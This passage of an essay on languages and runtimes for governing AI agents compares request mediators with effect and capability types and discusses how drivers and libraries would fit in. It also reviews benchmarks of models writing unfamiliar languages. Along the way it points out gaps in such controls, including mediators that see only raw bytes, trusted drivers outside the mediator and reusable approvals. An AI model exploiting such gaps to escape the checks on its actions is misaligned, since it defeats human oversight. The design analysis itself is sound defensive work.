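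A language's designers can choose which harmless programs it rejects. The language safescript requires programmers to write host names literally in the source. A checker can then read the source and list every host the program might contact, but it has to reject any program that computes an address at run time, even if every possible address is acceptable. Dhall makes the same tradeoff for its imports.

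The main practical question is how many useful programs a checker rejects. McCann expected a cautious checker to reject most ordinary Elixir code. The experiments with ELBA and TACIT suggest that few programs stay rejected when a language model writes new code for the checker and can read its error messages. They do not measure how much existing code would pass, which would matter more to a company with years of Python code.

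### Types before the run, a mediator during it

The designs differ more in when they act and who controls them than in what they can prevent.

| Question | Mashin | ELBA | TACIT | ETAS |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| When does it catch a violation? | When the program makes the request | Before the run for forbidden effects, during it for labels and file paths | Before the run for leaks of classified data, during it for file paths | Before the run if the compiler can settle the matter, otherwise at the request |
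| Can rules depend on run-time values? | Yes | Yes, through checks in the library | Yes, through checks in the library | Yes, through the host's check |
| Does it keep a record? | Yes, unless the program disables it | Only if a developer adds one | Only if a developer adds one | Yes, a trace of requests and outcomes |
| What do people have to write? | A list of permissions for each program | Types and operations for each policy | About 1,000 shared lines, then a few hundred for each set of tools | Effects and contracts for functions |
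| Who grants authority? | The operator, through the policy and trust levels | The developer who chooses the expected type | The developer who sets up the agent's environment | The developer who writes the contracts, and the host |

Authority that depends on types is hard to change quickly. If a company learns that an agent is misbehaving, an administrator can tighten a mediator's policy, and the new rule will apply to the next request. Changing a type, by contrast, affects only programs that the compiler checks afterward.

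A mediator may refuse a program's second step after the first has paid a customer. If Mashin had effect types, its compiler could compare the program's steps with its permissions and report a missing permission before any money moved. McCann says that a typed version of his calculus, which separates pure terms from those that make requests, is under development.

Mashin could also borrow the `Classified` wrapper. Its `compute` steps are already meant to be pure, so the runtime could let them work on a customer's card number while the compiler prevented the result from being put into a request. Only an operation the company had approved could remove the wrapper. This would stop many leaks that a permission check misses, but Mashin would first have to remove the clock and random numbers from `compute` steps.

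A mediator can also be added to a system that already tracks capabilities. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* names TACIT's library as the natural place to add audit logs and limits on how often an agent may act, but leaves both to future work. Every file and network operation already goes through that library, so adding a mediator there would not require changes to the agent's code.

Types cannot determine whether a refund will be for $120 or $350, but they can require a check when the program runs. The company could define a payment function that accepts only an `Approved Refund`, and let the mediator create such a value only after checking the amount or asking a manager. A program that skipped the approval would not compile. A program that compiled could still use the same approval twice, unless the mediator recorded which approvals had been used. *Language-Based Agent Control* suggests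 using linear types, which require a program to use a value exactly once, to make authorisations single-use.

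## What would it take to write real software in such a language?

Python programmers can import a package for almost any database, cloud service or file format. Packages that open connections or files could not be translated line by line into a governed language, because the lines that open them would have no equivalent.

Libraries that only calculate could keep their design. Some others would need small changes. For example, a date library that reads time-zone rules from a file could take the rules as an input instead. A library that opens connections itself would have to become either pure code that produces requests or a trusted part of the runtime.

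### A database driver, two ways

A database driver opens a network connection, logs in, sends each query in the database's own message format and decodes the rows that come back. Suppose the refund agent needs the total for order A-1041. If programmers wrote the driver in the governed language, a query would look roughly like this, leaving out login and encryption:

```
let opened = ask(open, "orders-db:5432", {}) in
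let sent   = ask(send, "orders-db:5432", {bytes: encode(query)}) in
let reply  = ask(receive, "orders-db:5432", {}) in
compute(decode(reply))
```

The pure functions `encode` and `decode` make up most of the driver. Programmers could write them, since pure code can do any calculation. A bug in `encode` could garble a query but could not send it to another server without a further request.

However, these requests would give the mediator little information. It could check that the program contacts only the orders database, but it would receive the query as bytes. To allow reads and refuse changes, it would need its own decoder for the database's format. That decoder would become part of the trusted computing base, and it would be useless if the driver encrypted its traffic. The program would also hold the database password. Even on an open connection, each query would take at least two requests,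 which would add more than a millisecond at Mashin's measured speed.

The alternative is to put an existing driver in the runtime and offer programs a single request:

```
let order = ask(find_order, "orders-db", {id: "A-1041"}) in
compute(order.total)
```

The mediator now receives an order number, which it can compare with the customer the agent is dealing with. The ledger entry is readable, and the password stays in the runtime. But the driver can use the network without making requests, so people have to trust it and everything it depends on, including its encryption library. A bug could make the driver run a different query from the one the mediator approved. An attacker who controlled the database could send a malformed reply that exploits a flaw in the decoder, then reach the policy and the ledger.

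Each new driver adds to this risk. A business program might also need a cache, a cloud file store, a message queue and a mail server. At the rate that Momeu and Sen found in Rust packages, all five drivers together would put about 56 bugs that cause undefined behaviour into the runtime. Programs might be unable to trigger most of these bugs through a request as narrow as `find_order`, but somebody would have to check whether that is true.

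A company can limit the damage by running each driver in its own process, which the operating system allows to contact only one database.

| | Driver in the governed language | Driver inside the mediator's process | Driver in its own process |
|---|---|---|---|
| What the mediator can check | The address and raw bytes | The order number | The order number |
| What holds the password | The program | The runtime | The driver's process |
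| What a hijacked driver could do | Make requests that the policy allows | Change the policy, erase records and use any connection | Read or change orders |

Clients for cloud services are easier to rebuild because most accept ordinary web requests, which pure code can construct. But many services require a signature, which the client calculates from the request and a secret key. The runtime would have to calculate this signature to keep the key from the program. The signing code would be a small trusted piece, and the rest of the client could stay pure.

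### How cheap has rebuilding become?

Coding agents have made this kind of rewriting much easier. Armin Ronacher, a Python developer, needed an Ethernet driver in JavaScript for a sandbox. Versions existed in Rust, C and Go, but Ronacher (2026) reports in *A Language For Agents* that having an agent write a new one was easier than connecting JavaScript to native code. He concludes that the breadth of a language's ecosystem now matters less.

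Tests of whole projects give mixed support. *Zero2Repo* (2026) gave agents a specification and an empty directory. GPT-6 Astra built 15 of 17 projects and Claude Opus 5.5 built 14, though many of the originals are well known, which probably raised the scores. *E2E-SWE* (2026) reports much lower scores on other projects, with network access disabled so that agents could not download the original code. Claude Opus 5 completed 22.1 percent of the projects and Claude Fable 5 completed 19.2 percent.

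An agent porting a driver can read the original, which should make the job easier than in the second test. But all of *Zero2Repo*'s tasks are in established languages, nine of them in Python, so the results may not carry over to a new one. Passing a project's tests also does not show that the code is secure. Rewriting with agents is therefore most useful for pure libraries, because the mediator still checks whatever a faulty library requests. A trusted driver needs careful review however easy it was to write.

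### Can models write a language they have hardly seen?

Language models write code badly in unfamiliar programming languages without documentation or extra training. In *No Resource, No Benchmarks, No Problem?*, Giagnorio, Martin-Lopez and Bavota (2026) tested GPT-4o and three other older models on Gleam and MoonBit, two general-purpose languages whose first stable versions appeared in 2024. Extra training on the little public code available raised scores on the hard problems from almost nothing to over 25 percent. *LLM-Based FORM Code Generation with Verification-Driven Fine-Tuning* (2026) found the same weakness in newer models. On one set of problems in FORM, a language for symbolic algebra, no model wrote a single valid program without documentation.

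In practice, developers would give the model documentation. Willison (2025) points out that the details of many languages fit in a few thousand tokens, and expects models to cope well if they can also run the compiler and correct their mistakes. Vera, a language Alasdair Allan designed for models to write, provides a test of learning from documentation. Its functions are pure unless their signatures declare effects such as web requests or model calls, so it resembles a governed language more than Gleam or FORM does. In Allan's VeraBench, models learned Vera from one document in the prompt.

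Two studies used *esoteric* languages, which their inventors made strange on purpose. Brainfuck, for example, has only eight commands. *EsoLang-Bench* (Sharma and Chopra, 2026) gave models problems in five of these languages, with documentation and at most five rounds of feedback. *Frontier Coding Agents Use Metaprogramming to Adapt to Unfamiliar Programming Languages* (Sharma, Thorat and Chopra, 2026) then gave agents the same problems in four of the five languages, with a workspace and unlimited use of an interpreter.

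| Test | Language | Help | Problems solved | In familiar languages |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Giagnorio and colleagues, hard problems | Gleam and MoonBit | None | 0–1% | 59–89% |
| *LLM-Based FORM Code Generation with Verification-Driven Fine-Tuning*, self-contained problems | FORM | None | 46.9% for GLM-5.3, the best model | Not given |
| VeraBench, three strongest models | Vera | One document | 88–100% | 86–96% in Python |
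| Sharma and Chopra | Five esoteric languages | Documentation, up to five rounds of feedback | 0–11% | 100% for the best models |
| Sharma and colleagues | Four esoteric languages | Workspace and interpreter | 11.3% for Kimi K2.5, 99.7% for GPT-5.4 | Not repeated |

Being able to run code greatly helped GPT-5.4, which solved at most 6.2 percent of the Brainfuck problems in the first study and 98.8 percent in the second.

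Kimi K2.5's results suggest that a language's strangeness matters more than its rarity. It solved every Vera problem after reading one document, but few problems in esoteric languages such as Brainfuck, even with an interpreter and even though Brainfuck, unlike Vera, had public code. However, the two sets of problems were different, and VeraBench has only 50, which Allan ran once per model. Models also had more trouble writing Vera's *contracts*, the conditions each function must satisfy. GPT-4.1's score fell from 91 to 50 percent when it had to work out the contracts from an English description.

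The best agents wrote Python programs that printed Brainfuck, and rarely wrote Brainfuck by hand. Python's variables and functions helped them keep track of details that are easy to lose in the raw code. With this method, Claude Opus 4.6 solved 64 of 80 problems and GPT-5.4 solved 79. When Sharma and colleagues forbade it, the two models solved 27 and 29. Written advice about the method did not help the weaker Claude Sonnet 4.6, which stayed at 12, but a small library of helper code raised its score to 64. Designers of a new language should therefore give agents working code as well as explanations.

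An agent could write programs in a governed language the same way, by running Python that prints them. The printed program could still act only by making requests, but the Python would need a sandbox.

Agents also use more tokens in less familiar languages. Wu, Anderson and Guha (2026), in *The Best Programming Language for Tokenmaxxing*, gave five models the same 100 problems in Python, Java, Rust and OCaml, with the tests visible. Accuracy was similar across languages, except that one small model did much worse in OCaml. For the same problem, agents produced 1.28 to 1.69 times as many tokens in OCaml as in Python, partly because they kept writing programs that would not compile.

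### Do agents need new languages?

Ronacher used to think that the huge amount of existing code would keep today's languages in place. He now expects more new languages, partly because porting code takes little effort and partly because an agent's success depends on more than training data. In his experience, agents struggle with Swift because of the tools for building Apple applications, even though models' training data includes plenty of Swift. They manage with Zig, which is rarer and changes quickly, if he points them to the right documentation.

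He also proposes that functions declare what they need from outside, for example with `needs { time, rng }` for the clock and random numbers. A formatting tool would add missing declarations to the functions' callers. The declarations would make effects visible and help an agent write tests with a fixed clock, but they would not restrict those effects. If an agent added a network call, the tool would update the callers' declarations to include it. In a governed language, someone other than the agent has to set the limits on effects.

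Laurence Tratt (2026), in *Local Reasoning for Global Properties*, argues that a language could help AI models if checks on each part of a program guaranteed a property of the whole. Models often write good individual functions but struggle when the code depends on understanding the whole program. Tratt used to answer "probably not" when people asked whether AI would benefit from new languages, because models already write almost any language.

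Tratt's example is Rust, whose compiler rejects *data races*, errors in which threads use the same data without coordination. He converted the program that builds his website to use several threads in under five minutes, and it worked the first time. A language without ungoverned effects gives the same kind of guarantee. A reviewer can rule out a direct network connection in one function without reading the rest of the program. Tratt accepts that models may soon overcome their weakness with large programs. The guarantee would still be useful then, because an agent that understands the whole program may be following an attacker's instructions.

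José Valim, who created Elixir, argues in *Evolving programming languages in the AI era* (2026) that agents help small language communities catch up by porting libraries, but also weaken the reason to share them, since anyone can ask an agent for a private version. This could be a serious problem for trusted drivers. If a hundred companies each generated their own database driver, each driver would have one user and few reviewers.

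Valim thinks a new language whose main attraction is agent-friendly syntax is built around the limits of today's models. He expects languages to compete more on their guarantees, including the boundaries a runtime enforces on capabilities. That argument supports governed effects, but a company can get such boundaries without a new language.

### A new language or part of an old one

Monty, an experimental interpreter for code that AI models write, runs a subset of Python. According to its documentation, Monty has its own virtual machine and cannot call C libraries. Pydantic, which develops Monty, says that programs start with no access to files, the network or environment variables. The application that runs a program grants each kind of access by supplying a function for it.

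A company could supply a `refund` function that sends every call to a mediator. If every other function it supplied did the same, all the program's external effects would be governed. Monty can also snapshot a running program, which could let a refund wait for a manager's approval. New JavaScript features let programs escape Caja's restrictions, but a new feature of standard Python could do the same in Monty only if Monty's developers implemented it.

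Much existing Python code cannot run in the subset. *pydantic-monty investigation* (Willison, 2026) reports that Monty leaves out large parts of standard Python, though unsupported features generally fail with clear errors. Packages that depend on C code cannot run in it. Pydantic plans to provide access to popular libraries, including the database engine DuckDB, through code in the host application. Each of these would be another trusted driver, and DuckDB is far larger than one that only passes queries to a server.

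A checked subset such as Joe-E keeps the original language's tools and the approved parts of its library.

| | New language, such as Mashin or Vera | Subset with its own interpreter, such as Monty | Checked subset, such as Joe-E |
|---|---|---|---|
| Existing pure code | Needs translation | Runs if it uses only supported features | Runs if it passes the checker |
| Existing drivers | Need rebuilding or trust | Need trusted functions in the host | Need safe wrappers |
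| Editors and other tools | Mostly new | Mostly the same | The same |
| Model fluency | Depends on documentation and feedback | High, apart from missing features | High, apart from forbidden features |
| Permissions and approvals | Can be part of the language | The host has to add them | Programmers have to add them |

Tools for a new language take time to build. Neward reported in June 2026 that Vera's package registry, editor plug-ins and language server, which gives editors information about code, were still unfinished. Interest is still growing. Vercel Labs introduced Zero, a systems language for agents, in May 2026. By August it had more than 5,200 stars on GitHub, according to InfoQ's *Vercel Labs Ships Zero* (2026), though stars are a better measure of curiosity than of use.

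For the refund agent, a subset of Python would take less work than a new language, because the agent's programs are short and need only a few operations, and current models already write Python fluently. A new language is easier to justify for a large program that many people and agents will change over several years, especially if its compiler can check effects before the program runs. With either approach, a company with a large existing Python system would have to rewrite most of the code that interacts with the outside world.
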